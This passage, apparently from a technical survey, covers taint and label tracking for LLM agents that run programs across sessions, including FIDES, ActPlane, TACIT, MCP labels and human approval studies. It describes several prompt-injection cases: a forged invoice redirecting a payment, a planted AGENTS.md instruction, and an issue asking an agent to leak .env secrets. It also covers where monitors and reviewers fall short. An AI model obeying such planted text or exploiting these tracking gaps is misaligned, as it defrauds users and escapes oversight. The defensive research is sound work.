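open("invoice.txt", "w").write(text)
print("Saved")
```

Its second program makes the payment:

```
text = open("invoice.txt").read()
account = text.split("Pay to:")[1].split()[0]
send_money(account, 1240)
```

The planner has seen only the word "Saved", so its context is still trusted. In the first program, the interpreter labels `text` as untrusted. But the file stores only characters, so when the second program reads it, Python creates a new string with no label. If the tracker treats unlabelled strings as trusted, a forged account number will pass the check in `send_money`.

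### What outlives a program

Programs can leave data in many places, and each needs its own way of keeping labels:

| What survives | Where the label could go | How the label can get lost |
|---|---|---|
| Interpreter variables | beside each value in memory | the system suspends the interpreter and saves only the values |
| Function definitions | on the function itself | a later program calls the function as if it were trusted code |
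| Files | in the file's metadata | a copy keeps the contents but not the metadata |
| Databases | in an extra column beside the data | other software adds a row and leaves that column empty |
| Caches | on each stored answer | the cache returns the answer alone |
| Remote services | in the metadata of requests and results | the service stores the text and later returns it as new data |

Variables are the simplest case as long as the same interpreter keeps running. TaintDroid, which Enck and colleagues (2014) built to follow private data through Android apps, stores a tag next to each variable in the interpreter's memory. To save space, it keeps only one tag per array, so one tainted item taints everything later read from that array. For agents, Girrens and Wang's SPA saves a label with every stored result, and TACIT can keep restrictions in the types of variables that last for a whole session.

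Functions need labels even when their arguments are trusted. Suppose a note planted in an invoice causes the planner to write a function, `parse_total`, that multiplies every total by ten. A new conversation then reuses the same container. Its planner starts with a trusted context and calls `parse_total` on a figure the user typed, which runs untrusted code on trusted data. The function should therefore keep the label of the context in which the planner wrote it, and the interpreter should add that label to the program-counter label during each call.

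Caches create a subtler problem because unrelated parts of a program may share an entry. Android's version of Java keeps one shared object for each whole number from −128 to 127. If a program converts a tainted 1 into an object, it receives the shared object for 1, which has no tag. Tagging that object would taint every other use of it. TaintDroid instead tags the program's reference to the object, so only the code that made the conversion gets a tainted result.

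### Files, shell commands and native code

TaintDroid's method of labeling files would have stopped the Harlow payment. TaintDroid stores a tag in each file's extended attributes, a small metadata area that many file systems provide. Writing to the file updates the tag, and reading the file copies the tag to the data that was read. Each file has only one tag, so a single untrusted line taints the whole file.

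The storage format must also support the tag. Android normally formatted memory cards as FAT, which can't hold extended attributes, so Enck and colleagues changed the phone software to support a different format. Git doesn't record extended attributes either, so if an agent commits `invoice.txt` and another machine downloads the repository, the text arrives without its tag.

TaintDroid also doesn't monitor native libraries, which run as compiled code outside the interpreter. For simple native functions, it gives the result the combined tags of all the arguments. This works for a function such as cosine, whose result depends only on its argument. It can fail when native code stores data inside an existing object, because a different call may return that data later.

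Shell commands are even harder to track. A command such as `make` takes few arguments but may read hundreds of files, so combining the labels of its arguments would miss most of its inputs. It may also run a script that an earlier program wrote. A tracker inside Python can observe the command and its printed output, but not the files it opens.

### Tracking in the operating system

The operating system handles every file that a shell command opens, so several recent systems track labels there. They use eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small, checked programs inside the kernel whenever a process starts, opens a file or makes a connection.

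*ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) attaches labels to processes, files and network addresses. A process that reads a file of access keys takes on that file's label, then passes it to any process it starts and any file it writes. A rule can stop a process with that label from connecting to an outside address, even if the agent started the process through several layers of scripts.

Zheng and colleagues measured what tracking at the level of tool calls misses. They took 38 rules from real software projects, such as running the tests before committing a change, and generated 190 records of agents keeping or breaking them. ActPlane detected 77.2 percent of the violations. FIDES and two other defences that check tool calls detected between 34 and 40 percent, and almost none when the violation happened inside a harmless-looking script. The violations were breaches of project rules, not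 prompt injections, so the figures don't measure how often these defences stop attacks.

*Agent-Warden*, by Cui, Gu and colleagues (2026), tests a case closer to the saved invoice. An agent starts a script that writes a temporary file, another process renames the file, and a separate monitoring script on the same machine later reads it. An ordinary log of the agent's activity ended before the monitoring script read the file. Agent-Warden reconstructed the whole chain in all 120 runs because it attaches its mark to the inode, the kernel's record of a file, which stays the same when the file is renamed.

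Agent-Warden keeps these marks in memory, so they disappear when the computer restarts and can disappear when memory runs short. It also can't observe pipes, which usually carry a shell command's output back to the program that ran it. When a marked process ends, Agent-Warden marks its parent too, whether or not the parent used the output. This only partly makes up for not seeing pipes, because the parent could have read the output and passed it on before being marked.

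*AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) uses labels that identify the exchange with the model that led to each action. In one test, an agent wrote a malicious instruction into `AGENTS.md`, a file that coding agents load for guidance. A later session followed the instruction and ran a shell command, which AgentLoupe traced back to the session that had written the file. To stop labels from spreading everywhere, AgentLoupe gives each new user prompt a fresh identifier and records a link to the old one. The link is enough for an investigator, but a system that blocked actions would have to follow it, or it would treat the second session as untainted. Bao and colleagues haven't yet measured how often their labels miss a real connection or add a false one.

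These systems slow agents down very little. ActPlane added 1.9 percent to the running time of a replayed agent session and up to 8.4 percent to a large compilation job. Agent-Warden added between 0.2 and 3.5 percent, and AgentLoupe at most 8 percent. Imprecise labels are a bigger problem than the slowdown. The kernel treats a Python interpreter as one process, so once any program running in it reads `invoice.txt`, every file the interpreter writes afterwards becomes tainted. Zheng and colleagues suggest starting a fresh process to clear accumulated labels, which is safe only if nothing from the old process goes into the new one.

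### Recovering dependencies between programs

Finer tracking has to take place inside the interpreter. *FlowBook* (Freund, Berger and colleagues, 2026) shows how to recover dependencies between pieces of code that run separately but share variables. It works on computational notebooks, which are documents made of code cells that a user can edit and run in any order. FlowBook is meant to make results reproducible and has no security labels, but a notebook's cells are much like the successive programs an agent runs in the same interpreter.

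In one of their examples, a scientist corrects air-quality readings by multiplying them by 1.8, then changes the factor to 1.85 and runs the cell again. The cell multiplies the already corrected readings by the new factor, so the total correction is 3.33. An ordinary notebook doesn't warn the scientist that the resulting chart is wrong.

FlowBook catches this by recording, for each cell $i$, a read set $R_i$ of the variables the cell took from earlier code and a write set $W_i$ of the variables it changed. It copies the notebook's variables before the cell runs and compares them with the originals afterwards, so it finds changes made by native libraries as well as by Python. It conservatively counts reading a variable as reading everything reachable from it. The correction cell overwrites the same readings it takes as input, so FlowBook blocks it and restores the earlier values.

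A security tracker could use the same two sets to carry labels from one program to the next. Let $c_i$ be the context label when the planner writes program $i$, and $s_i$ the combined label of any tool results the program fetches. Every variable $w$ in $W_i$ would then get the label

$$\lambda(w) = c_i \sqcup s_i \sqcup \bigsqcup_{r \in R_i} \lambda(r).$$

For example, suppose the planner's context is trusted throughout and `budget` comes from the user's own records:

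| Program | Reads | Writes | Label of what it writes |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | the result of `get_invoice` | `invoice` | untrusted |
| 2 | `invoice` | `amount` | untrusted |
| 3 | `budget` | `limit` | trusted |
| 4 | `amount`, `limit` | `over_limit` | untrusted |

`limit` stays trusted even though the interpreter already holds an untrusted invoice, which tracking by process would not allow. Labels are still coarse within each program, because everything a program writes is treated as depending on everything it reads. FlowBook reduces this problem for tables by treating each column as a separate location, so a supplier's price column would not have to taint a column of the user's own stock figures.

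Freund and colleagues ran FlowBook on 61 public data-science notebooks with 999 cells in total. It flagged 203 cells whose results could depend on execution order. Reruns confirmed that 126 of these could change a visible result, and only 11 were false alarms. The checks added a median of 26 milliseconds per cell, but were slow when FlowBook had to copy and compare very large data, such as a 4.3-gigabyte matrix.

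Those results show that recording reads and writes is practical for ordinary Python code, but not that it would withstand an attacker. Comparing variables before and after a run has the gap that Fenton found in monitors. If a secret condition makes a program skip a change, the comparison finds nothing to label. To close the gap, the tracker would have to relabel everything the program could have changed, which in Python may be every variable the program can reach.

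FlowBook also runs in the same Python process as the code it checks, so hostile code could try to alter its records. It skips any cell that the user marks as diagnostic, and an agent could write that mark itself. It records files that a cell opens through Python's own functions, but a shell command can open files without those functions. These gaps matter little to a scientist who wants a correct chart and has no reason to evade the tool.

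### Labels in tool calls

Neither an interpreter nor a kernel can follow data into a remote service, so the agent has to send labels with its requests and the service has to send them with its results. Microsoft and GitHub have built a prototype that does this with the Model Context Protocol (MCP), whose messages already have a field called `_meta` for extra information. Software that doesn't support labels can ignore the field.

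A request to post a message in a Teams channel might include these labels, with names in place of the real user numbers:

```
"_meta": {
  "com.github.ifc/labels": {
    "$": {
      "integrity": "untrusted",
      "confidentiality": "public"
    },
    "$.arguments.content": {
      "integrity": "trusted",
      "confidentiality": ["Alex", "Priya"]
    }
  }
}
```

The keys use JSONPath, a notation for pointing to parts of structured data. `$` stands for the whole request, and Copilot CLI puts its context label there. `$.arguments.content` is the text of the message. The request as a whole is untrusted, perhaps because the planner has read an outsider's email, but the text came from a trusted source and only Alex and Priya may read it.

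A part without its own label inherits the label of the part that contains it, so the channel number in this request is untrusted and public. An unlabelled container also takes its label from its contents, so a list containing both Priya's and Marco's emails to Alex would be readable only by Alex. An agent could still store the two emails in separate variables, each with its own label.

An explicit label on a container takes priority over the labels inside it. In the Teams example, a policy that checked only `$` would find the label "public" and could allow a private message to go to the entire channel. The policy has to check the text's own label. Microsoft's sample policy does this, then gets the channel's current members from the Teams server and compares them with the permitted readers.

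GitHub's own server labels only the result as a whole. For private repositories, it sends the word "private" instead of a list of readers. According to the package documentation on pkg.go.dev, the agent's software looks up the readers when the agent is about to send something out. The list is therefore up to date even if a collaborator leaves the project between runs. But the agent's software has to record which repository each value came from. If it saved only the word "private" with a file, a later program couldn't look up who was allowed to read it.

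### Tools that don't support labels

Most tools don't send labels, so Microsoft has released a gateway that sits between the tools and the agent. For each tool, a developer describes the format of the results, writes a Python function that computes their labels from the tool's arguments, and supplies or selects a policy.

Microsoft also describes a fallback that needs no code for individual tools. It uses annotations, short descriptions of a tool's behaviour that MCP already supports:

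| Annotation | Possible policy |
|---|---|
| Only reads data, within a closed system | always allow |
| Only reads data, but contacts the outside world | allow if all arguments are public |
| May destroy data | ask the user |

For labels, the fallback assumes that every argument may end up in the result. It also marks results as untrusted if the tool contacts the outside world, and as private if the tool requires a login. A web search with a private query would return a private, untrusted result.

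This rule can lose a label when a tool stores data between calls. Suppose the first Harlow program saves the invoice with a note-taking tool on the user's computer, and the second program calls `read_note(7)`. The number 7 is trusted and public, and the tool doesn't contact the outside world or require a login. The fallback therefore wouldn't mark the result as untrusted, even though the note contains the forged account number. For tools that store data, the system would also have to join the labels of everything earlier programs had saved in them.

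The annotations may also be false. The Model Context Protocol project explains in an official blog post (2026) that annotations are hints, which the agent's software must treat as untrusted unless it has reason to trust the server. A malicious server could describe a tool that forwards its arguments to an attacker as a closed, read-only tool, which the first policy in the table would always allow. It could just as easily supply false labels. The same post lists a proposal for standard trust and sensitivity annotations, which was still a draft in March 2026. A standard would make labels easier to exchange, but the agent's software would still have to decide which servers to trust.

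### Requirements for tracking across runs

To track taint across runs, a system needs stable identities for values, labels stored with the data, a rule for unlabelled data, and monitoring of every path that data can take from one program to the next.

A label needs a stable identifier for the item it describes. File names are unsuitable because a program can rename a file or put new contents under an old name. Process numbers and the memory addresses of Python objects are also unreliable because the computer reuses them. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) ties labels to particular versions of files and stored objects, so new contents don't inherit the label of the version they replaced. *PerMIT* (2026), a design for agent memory, forbids changes to stored entries. If a user reads an untrusted entry and confirms it, the system creates a separate trusted copy and leaves the original untrusted.

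The system that stores the data should also store its label, and should save both in one step. If it saves them separately, a crash between the two saves could leave an invoice on disk without its label. A later check can't restore the label. *Safety in Self-Evolving Agents* (2026) points out that examining the wording of a retrieved memory can't recover a source the system discarded when it saved the memory. Copies and backups need the labels too, and Agent libOS keeps them when a process saves its state, sends a message or starts another process.

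Generated code must not be able to remove labels. TaintDroid lets apps add tags but gives them no function for clearing one. Labels stored in an ordinary Linux file's extended attributes are less protected, because a program running as the file's owner can usually delete them. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) discusses storage formats that reveal when someone has altered an entry in an agent's memory. These could expose a changed label, but not whether the original entry was harmful.

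Some data will always arrive without a label, because it is older than the tracker or because a server failed to send one. The safe default is to treat it as both untrusted and private. Applying this default to a whole computer would make almost every existing file untrusted and cause label creep. A system can avoid some of this by adding a component built to label data from a particular source. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* calls such components guards. A guard for GitHub labels its data, and a small separate monitor compares those labels with what the agent may read or write. FlowBook is stricter with the few objects it can't copy, such as open file handles, and blocks later cells from reading them.

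Monitoring every path is the hardest requirement to meet. A tracker in the interpreter follows variables but not shell commands, while a tracker in the kernel follows files but can't distinguish the variables inside one process. Even with both, remote services could still return stored text without a label. Agent libOS covers many of these paths, but Zhang doesn't claim that it provides noninterference.

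A simpler approach is to give the whole container one label and join it with the label of everything that enters. Everything that leaves the container, whether through a file, a shell command or a tool call, carries that label. The system only has to monitor the container's boundary, and it doesn't matter that `invoice.txt` can't hold its own label. But after the first Harlow program runs, the container can't make any payment that requires trusted data, even to an account number the user typed. The agent would have to make that payment from a fresh container, without copying over any variables, functions or files from the old one.

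## Letting selected information back to the planner

A planner often needs only one fact from an untrusted result. For example, repairing a failed build may depend on whether a package was missing or a test failed, but not on the exact words of the log. If the planner reads the whole log, the context label marks everything it writes afterwards as untrusted. FIDES, the agent that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the planner choose how much of a result to read.

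### Hiding, querying and revealing

In FIDES, by Costa and colleagues, the planner requests one tool call at a time. When a result comes back, FIDES compares each field's label with the context label. The planner sees the fields that wouldn't make the context label more restrictive. FIDES stores the others in variables and shows the planner only the variables' names. For example, the planner might see an email's date but only the name `#read_emails_0.body#` in place of its text.

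The planner then has three options:

| Option | What the planner learns | Effect on the context label |
|---|---|---|
| Pass the variable to a tool | nothing about its contents | none |
| Ask the quarantined model about it | nothing yet, because the answer goes into a new variable | none |
| Reveal a variable | everything in that variable | joins with the variable's label |

The second and third options are most useful together. In one of the paper's examples, a user asks the agent to read the top three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting:

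1. The planner calls `read_emails`, and the emails go into a variable.
2. It asks the quarantined model whether they contain a meeting request, and requires a yes or no.
3. It reveals that answer.
4. If the answer is yes, it asks the quarantined model for the event's details, which go into another variable.
5. It passes that variable to `set_event` without reading it.

Constrained decoding enforces the format of the answer in step 2. As the quarantined model writes, the software rules out every token that would break that format. An instruction planted in an email can still change a "no" to a "yes", but it can't add a sentence for the planner to read.

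The "yes" is still untrusted, since anyone who can send an email can influence it. FIDES adds a type to the label, such as $((U, \text{public}), \text{bool})$, and orders the types by how much information they can carry, with Booleans lowest, then choices from a fixed list, then free text. A policy can then let an untrusted Boolean influence the decision to create an event, but not an untrusted string.

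An agent that writes code could use the same method on the Harlow Plumbing invoice, where the planner needed the format of the total before it could write a parser. The agent could check whether the total is formatted like 1,240.00 or 1.240,00, reveal only that choice to the planner, and have it write a matching parser. A forged invoice could cause the wrong choice and therefore the wrong amount, but it couldn't add a line to the program. The account number would stay in its variable with an untrusted label, and `send_money` would still reject it.

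Hidden results can inform the planner even when it can't read them. In one Slack task, a user asks the agent to add Alice to the channel with the fewest messages. A simpler version of FIDES, without the quarantined model, hid the channel names and the text of every message. But the planner could still count the variables in each list, so it found an empty channel and passed that channel's hidden name to the tool. Anyone who can post messages can change those counts, so the decision depended on untrusted data even though the context label stayed trusted.

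### Results and limits of FIDES

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo against a basic agent with one context label. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed without attacks, using OpenAI's o1 model:

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent, no policy checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| Basic agent, policy checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
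| FIDES, policy checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

With checks on, FIDES completed an average of 16 percentage points more tasks than the basic agent across the four environments. With GPT-4o, the gain was 8 points. Travel was the exception. Many of its tools may run in an untrusted context as long as they reveal nothing private, so hiding results complicated the work with little benefit. FIDES still completed about 23 points fewer tasks than an agent with no checks. Many of the lost tasks ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policies are meant to block.

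In the security tests, which used GPT-4o, attacks succeeded 152 times against the basic agent and 21 times against FIDES when both ran without checks. With checks on, no attacks succeeded against either agent, after Costa and colleagues excluded cases that they considered harmless or that AgentDojo had misjudged. Hiding untrusted text therefore prevented most attacks by itself, but the planner could still reveal the text and follow instructions in it.

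Two qualifications to these results matter for tracking across runs. The tested version of FIDES left out constrained decoding because few AgentDojo tasks needed it, so the results provide almost no evidence about typed labels. The tests also used a looser policy than the basic one for consequential actions. For tools such as `send_money`, it checked the label on the decision to call the tool but ignored the labels on the arguments, so a planner that passed Harlow's forged account number in a variable would have satisfied it.

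The FIDES theorem has a related gap because it establishes only explicit secrecy. It doesn't cover what an observer learns from the order of the calls, their timing or the size of network messages. A constrained answer mainly affects which call the agent makes next. For example, if a policy lets a private yes-or-no answer decide whether the agent sends a public message, the theorem doesn't limit what that decision reveals.

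### The release in Agent Framework

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced FIDES on 20 May as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents. By default, the framework hides every untrusted result behind a reference. When the agent needs a summary or a detail from a result, the framework sends that result to a quarantined model. If a developer switches hiding off, the main model reads the raw text and the context label provides the protection.

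The announcement's example, which has hiding turned off, resembles the earlier attack on coding assistants connected to GitHub. In the example, the planted issue tells the agent to post the contents of `.env`, a file that often holds passwords. The comment tool accepts only public data, so once the agent has read the file, the framework blocks the comment or, if the developer has set it to, asks a person whether to allow it.

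One weakness Microsoft lists is that the framework treats a tool without labels as trusted and public, so a developer who forgets to label an email reader gets no protection from that tool's results. The safe default would be to treat unlabeled tools as untrusted and private. The quarantined model can also answer only one question at a time.

The framework also labels all of the quarantined model's output as untrusted, whatever its type, so revealing a yes-or-no answer would currently taint the context as much as revealing the whole issue. Microsoft describes constrained decoding as a future step in a separate article.

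A single question may not be enough to diagnose a build, because the model might need to read the log, open a configuration file and then read the log again. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev et al., 2026) lets an agent start a temporary copy of itself for such work. The copy inherits the conversation, reads whatever it needs, and accumulates the untrusted labels. It can return only a value from a fixed set, after which the original agent continues with its old context label. In 1,320 test runs with these protections on, the researchers observed no successful attacks, and the agent completed between 64.2 and 91 percent of tasks. Discarding the copy doesn't undo its effects on the outside world, so its tool calls need the same checks as the original's.

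### Counting bits

*L3M*, a design for agents that extend their own abilities, uses a simple bound for answers from a fixed list. As *L3M* (2026) puts it, a choice among $N$ options carries at most $\log_2 N$ bits, however much the model read in order to choose. For a series of answers with $N_1, \dots, N_k$ options, the limits add up:

$$\log_2 N_1 + \log_2 N_2 + \dots + \log_2 N_k.$$

Suppose the planner gives the quarantined model eight possible causes for the failed build. The answer carries at most 3 bits, because $2^3 = 8$. Ten such answers carry up to 30 bits, enough to pick out one of about a billion possibilities:

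| Choices among eight | Most they can carry | Enough to specify |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 3 bits | one of eight repairs |
| 5 | 15 bits | any four-digit PIN |
| 9 | 27 bits | any eight-digit account number |
| 10 | 30 bits | any of 1,073,741,824 values |

A release that is safe once may therefore be unsafe when repeated. Nine answers could reveal a private account number in full. They could also let an attacker supply an account number, if the planner assembled it from the answers. A sensible planner has no reason to do this, but a planner that keeps asking questions until a build succeeds may release many bits without anyone intending it.

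FIDES's typed labels can't detect this build-up. The join of two Booleans is

$$\text{bool} \sqcup \text{bool} = \text{bool},$$

so a context that has absorbed 30 untrusted yes-or-no answers has the same type as one that has absorbed a single answer. Any join behaves this way, since joining a label with itself changes nothing. A system that wants to limit the total needs a separate counter.

*L3M* proposes a ledger that counts private data toward possible leakage when the agent reads it. Once the model has processed the data, the parts of its output have no separate labels, so the system can no longer tell what to count. An agent that reads 64 bytes of private data and then sends two 50-byte messages can have leaked at most 64 bytes, not 100. For smaller releases, the public side of the system offers a list of options and the private side returns only its choice.

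Setting a useful limit is hard. *Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) studies how a person can get help from a cloud model without uploading private documents. Its system keeps a ledger of how much each released answer could reveal. A limit of 16 nats (about 23 bits) per answer preserved most of the system's benefit on a question-answering test. The paper acknowledges that this limit is too loose to protect a short secret. A six-digit security code, for example, contains only about 20 bits.

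The bound also depends on the options coming from trusted data. If the log supplied the list of causes, an attacker could write an instruction as one of the options. Failures count as answers too, so if the quarantined model can also return a fixed error message, a choice among eight has nine outcomes and carries up to 3.17 bits. If the model writes the error message itself, there is no useful limit on how much information the message can carry.

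### Who may trigger a release

Some tasks need more than a few bits of information. Harlow's payment needs the full account number, and a quarterly sales report needs the figures. Endorsement and declassification handle these cases by overriding the label, so it matters a great deal what can trigger them.

Suppose an agent has read an email that tells it to send the sales figures to an outside address. If the planner could then declassify the figures, the attacker could cause the release by asking for it. The usual rule, robust declassification, therefore permits a release only when the decision comes from a trusted context. Garby and colleagues apply the same principle to endorsement, so endorsement has no effect in a program written after an untrusted read.

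An attacker can choose what data is released even when the decision to release it is trusted. Suppose Alex asks an agent to post a summary of three emails in a Teams channel, and one email contains a planted instruction to include Priya's sales figures. The planner never reads the emails, so its context stays trusted. The quarantined model does read them, and it follows the instruction and includes the figures. Microsoft's sample policy for Teams would allow the post, because it lets any call from a trusted context send text to people who aren't permitted to read it. The more permissive policy in the FIDES tests has the same weakness.

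A stricter policy could also require the text to be trusted whenever a message would reach someone outside its reader set. The agent could still post an untrusted summary to people who were already entitled to read all three emails, but Alex would have to approve sending it to anyone else.

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) gives this decision to another model, which receives the protected records and the proposed output and answers SAFE only if the two are unrelated in meaning. The paper reports very low leakage rates but notes that a wrong answer can leak data. The check also misses implicit flows. For example, a message containing only "see you on Tuesday" is unrelated in meaning to a medical record, even if the agent chose Tuesday instead of Wednesday because of the record's contents.

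### One recipient and one payload

How long a release lasts matters as much as what triggers it. If Alex approves one message to Marco about the sales figures and the system marks the figures as public, every later program can send them to anyone.

Agent libOS, the agent runtime by Zhang, avoids this by leaving the label alone. When data is too sensitive for a destination's normal clearance, but still within the maximum its rule allows, the system can ask a person for a release that works once. The release covers:

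- the process and the operation that asked for it
- the recipient
- a digest of the exact payload, which changes if any character changes
- the versions of the files or objects the data came from, and their labels
- a deadline.

Agent libOS checks these details again just before sending. If a later program rewrites the message, replaces Marco's address or uses an updated spreadsheet, the release no longer applies. If a crash leaves it unclear whether the message went out, the system treats the release as used and doesn't resend the message automatically. APPA similarly ties each approval to one exact tool call, and Kravchenko and colleagues prove that the approval doesn't authorize later calls.

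The release can't make data more trustworthy. Agent libOS lets an operation set a minimum level of integrity, and permission to share a secret doesn't waive that minimum. A person who allows Harlow's account number to leave the computer isn't confirming that the number belongs to Harlow. A process needs a separate administrative permission to change a label permanently, and the model can't request that permission through its ordinary memory tools.

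These limits narrow a release, but they don't ensure that it is a good decision. The digest ensures that Marco receives the message Alex approved, but Alex may have approved it without reading it, and Marco can forward it.

### How often the system needs a person

When a person approves a call that a policy blocked, the approval also releases information. Its value depends on how often the system requires approval and how carefully people review the requests.

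*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) measures the first of these on AgentDojo and introduces Prudentia, an extension of FIDES that tells the planner about labels and policies so that it can avoid unnecessary blocks. Before revealing untrusted data, the planner has to explain why it needs the data and list the calls it expects to make next. The planner can then either accept the taint or ask the user to endorse the data.

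Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email with ten tasks, each of which needs a trusted context. The user faces ten approval requests if the planner reveals the email without endorsement, but only one if the user endorses it first. The researchers left out an equivalent option for declassification, because whether information is appropriate to share depends on who will receive it and why.

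With GPT-5 and no attacks, the four agents they compared performed as follows:

| Agent | Tasks completed without asking | Tasks completed with unlimited requests | Requests in completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| Context label | 43.4% | 72.3% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

The last column shows the average number of requests in one pass through the benchmark's 97 tasks. Prudentia needed about one request for every eleven tasks it completed, compared with about three for every four when the agent asked before every consequential action. The improvement depends on the model. With GPT-4o, Prudentia made 23.8 requests, compared with 7.8 for FIDES, and completed fewer tasks without help.

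Replacing ten approvals with one endorsement can make a malicious task easier to miss, which these figures don't measure. Someone who approves ten calls sees each action and can refuse any that look wrong, whereas someone who endorses an email has to notice an eleventh task planted in its text. If they miss it, the policy that requires a trusted context will no longer stop it. Kolluri and colleagues assume that people would recognise and refuse harmful requests, and leave the design of the requests to future work.

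### How carefully people review

Recent evidence makes that assumption doubtful. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97 percent of permission prompts. Most prompts are probably for safe commands, so this doesn't prove carelessness. But in an experiment Anthropic ran, 1,053 paid testers worked on coding tasks, and one prompt in each session showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 percent of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17 percent early in a session to about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts.

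The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than a real developer. Anthropic was also arguing for auto mode, in which a classifier reviews actions in place of the user. The classifier blocked 89 percent of the same commands. It is probabilistic and can't provide the guarantees that labels can, but on this evidence it reviews commands much better than a tired person does.

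*From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026) cites findings that people pay less attention to warnings as they repeat. Experienced Claude Code users turn on automatic approval more often, but they also interrupt the agent more often, so some may be supervising by interrupting instead of approving each action. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, the user had switched to automatic approval. In 31, the prompt didn't give the user enough information to judge the action.

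The second problem is particularly serious for agents that write code. Approving a routine-looking prompt to run `python3 setup.py` authorises whatever the script contains, including anything the planner wrote after reading an untrusted page. A label could improve the prompt by showing that the script depends on an issue filed by an outsider and can access private files. None of these studies tested whether people would make better decisions with that information.

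People seem more likely to reject larger decisions. Anthropic found that users reject 39 percent of the plans Claude presents, compared with 3 percent of individual permission requests. They may reject many plans for reasons unrelated to security, such as disliking the design. Still, the gap somewhat supports asking users rarely and only about substantial decisions, as Prudentia does when it requests one endorsement in place of ten approvals.

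### Small answers without a label

People review poorly, so a system might instead let small answers through with no label or approval. Costa and colleagues consider a Boolean unlikely to lead to a prompt injection by itself, and a less restrictive policy could ignore its taint.

The failed build offers a good argument for letting the answer back to the planner. If the log's author can only choose one of eight causes, the planner still writes the repair in its own words. A single-shot program with a branch for each cause would give the author the same choice, and control-flow integrity already permits that. The multi-shot planner writes one branch after receiving the answer instead of writing all eight beforehand. Labelling the answer as untrusted would block the repair, and the only power it would take from the log's author is one that a fixed program would also give.

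The comparison weakens as the answers accumulate. Ten answers, each chosen from eight options, correspond to a program with more than a billion paths, too many for a planner to write in advance or a person to inspect. The planner also chooses each new question after receiving the last answer, so early false answers can lead it to ask about the wrong files and offer only options that lead to harm.

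A single bit can also determine what the planner does. If the planner's query is whether Harlow's new bank details have already been verified, a forged invoice that produces a "yes" is enough to make the planner skip its own comparison. Kravchenko and colleagues similarly point out that a fixed set of answers limits what a compromised temporary copy can return, but the copy can still pick a false one. Treating the answer as trusted is therefore a separate decision by the developer. One bit is also enough to violate privacy by disclosing whether somebody has a particular illness.

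The number of bits measures how many outcomes an attacker can select, not how bad the worst of them is. This is a reason to keep the untrusted label together with the type, as FIDES's design does, and to set what each tool accepts in that tool's policy. The policy for a tool that edits a separate copy of the source code could allow a program influenced by one untrusted choice among eight, because a developer can discard the copy. The policy for `send_money` could block the same program. If the system had removed the label when it released the answer, neither policy could take into account that the program depended on the log.

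## Checking each new program before it runs

Most of the policies described so far act when a program calls a tool. A type checker, which is part of a compiler, can check the program before it runs. It rejects any program that uses a value in a way its type doesn't allow, such as dividing a number by a date. SPA, by Girrens and Wang, also checks plans in advance, but its planner has only six kinds of step and can't retry. With a type checker, an agent can write ordinary code after each result and correct it if the compiler rejects it.

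### A wrapper for secrets

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) presents TACIT, a system that treats the agent's model and every program it writes as potentially hostile. The agent writes in Scala 3, using an experimental feature called capture checking. Here, a capability is a program value, such as a file handle or a network connection, that permits an effect. (CaMeL uses the same word for its labels.) Code can't write to a file without that file's capability, and capture checking records in each function's type which capabilities the function can use.

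Secret data arrives in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can't open the wrapper, but it can pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the contents and wraps the result again. `map` accepts only pure functions, which hold no capabilities and so can't print, write to a file or use the network.

This program compiles:

```
requestFileSystem("/secrets") {
  val key = readClassified("/secrets/github.txt")
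  val size = key.map { k => k.length }
  println(size)
}
```

The user's terminal shows the real length of the key, while the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. In one test, an agent wrote a program much like this one instead:

```
requestFileSystem("/secrets") {
  val key = readClassified("/secrets/github.txt")
  key.map { k => println(k) }
}
```

Printing needs a capability, so the compiler gives the function a type like `String ->{io} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The program doesn't compile, so none of it runs, including the line that reads the key.

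Ordinary Scala has features, such as unchecked casts, that let a program override its types. TACIT compiles agent code in a subset of Scala that forbids these features. Scala's documentation page for the subset, *Safe Mode*, recommends it for code written by agents.

When a task requires understanding secret text, the program can send the wrapped text to a separate trusted model, which returns a wrapped answer. Odersky and colleagues assume that this model does not retain the text it processes.

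### Typed sessions

TACIT works with any agent that supports MCP, including Claude Code and GitHub Copilot. It can run each program in a fresh interpreter or keep a session in which variables and functions persist. In a session, the compiler checks each new program against everything the earlier ones defined.

Suppose a user asks for a summary of a secret contract. The agent's first program has the trusted model write it:

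```
val summary = requestFileSystem("/data") {
  val doc = readClassified("/data/secret/contract.txt")
  chat("Summarize:", doc)
}
```

The user then asks how long the summary is, and the agent writes `println(summary.map(_.length))`. The compiler still treats `summary` as a `Classified[String]`, so the second program can't reveal its text to the agent either. The permission to read files is valid only inside the block that requested it. If the first program tried to save a function that still held that permission, the compiler would reject the program.

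The variable's type is therefore a confidentiality label that persists between runs, and the agent can't remove it by writing different code. Odersky and colleagues argue that in systems such as CaMeL, a value loses its label once it enters the model's conversation, whereas TACIT never puts the secret there. The criticism is fair for trackers that label only variables. A label on the context would still record that the planner had read something secret, but not which later values depended on it.

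Types offer less protection when the problem is trust. The `parse_total` function, which multiplied every total by ten because of a note in an invoice, is pure and has the same type as a correct parser. A later program in the session could call it and still compile.

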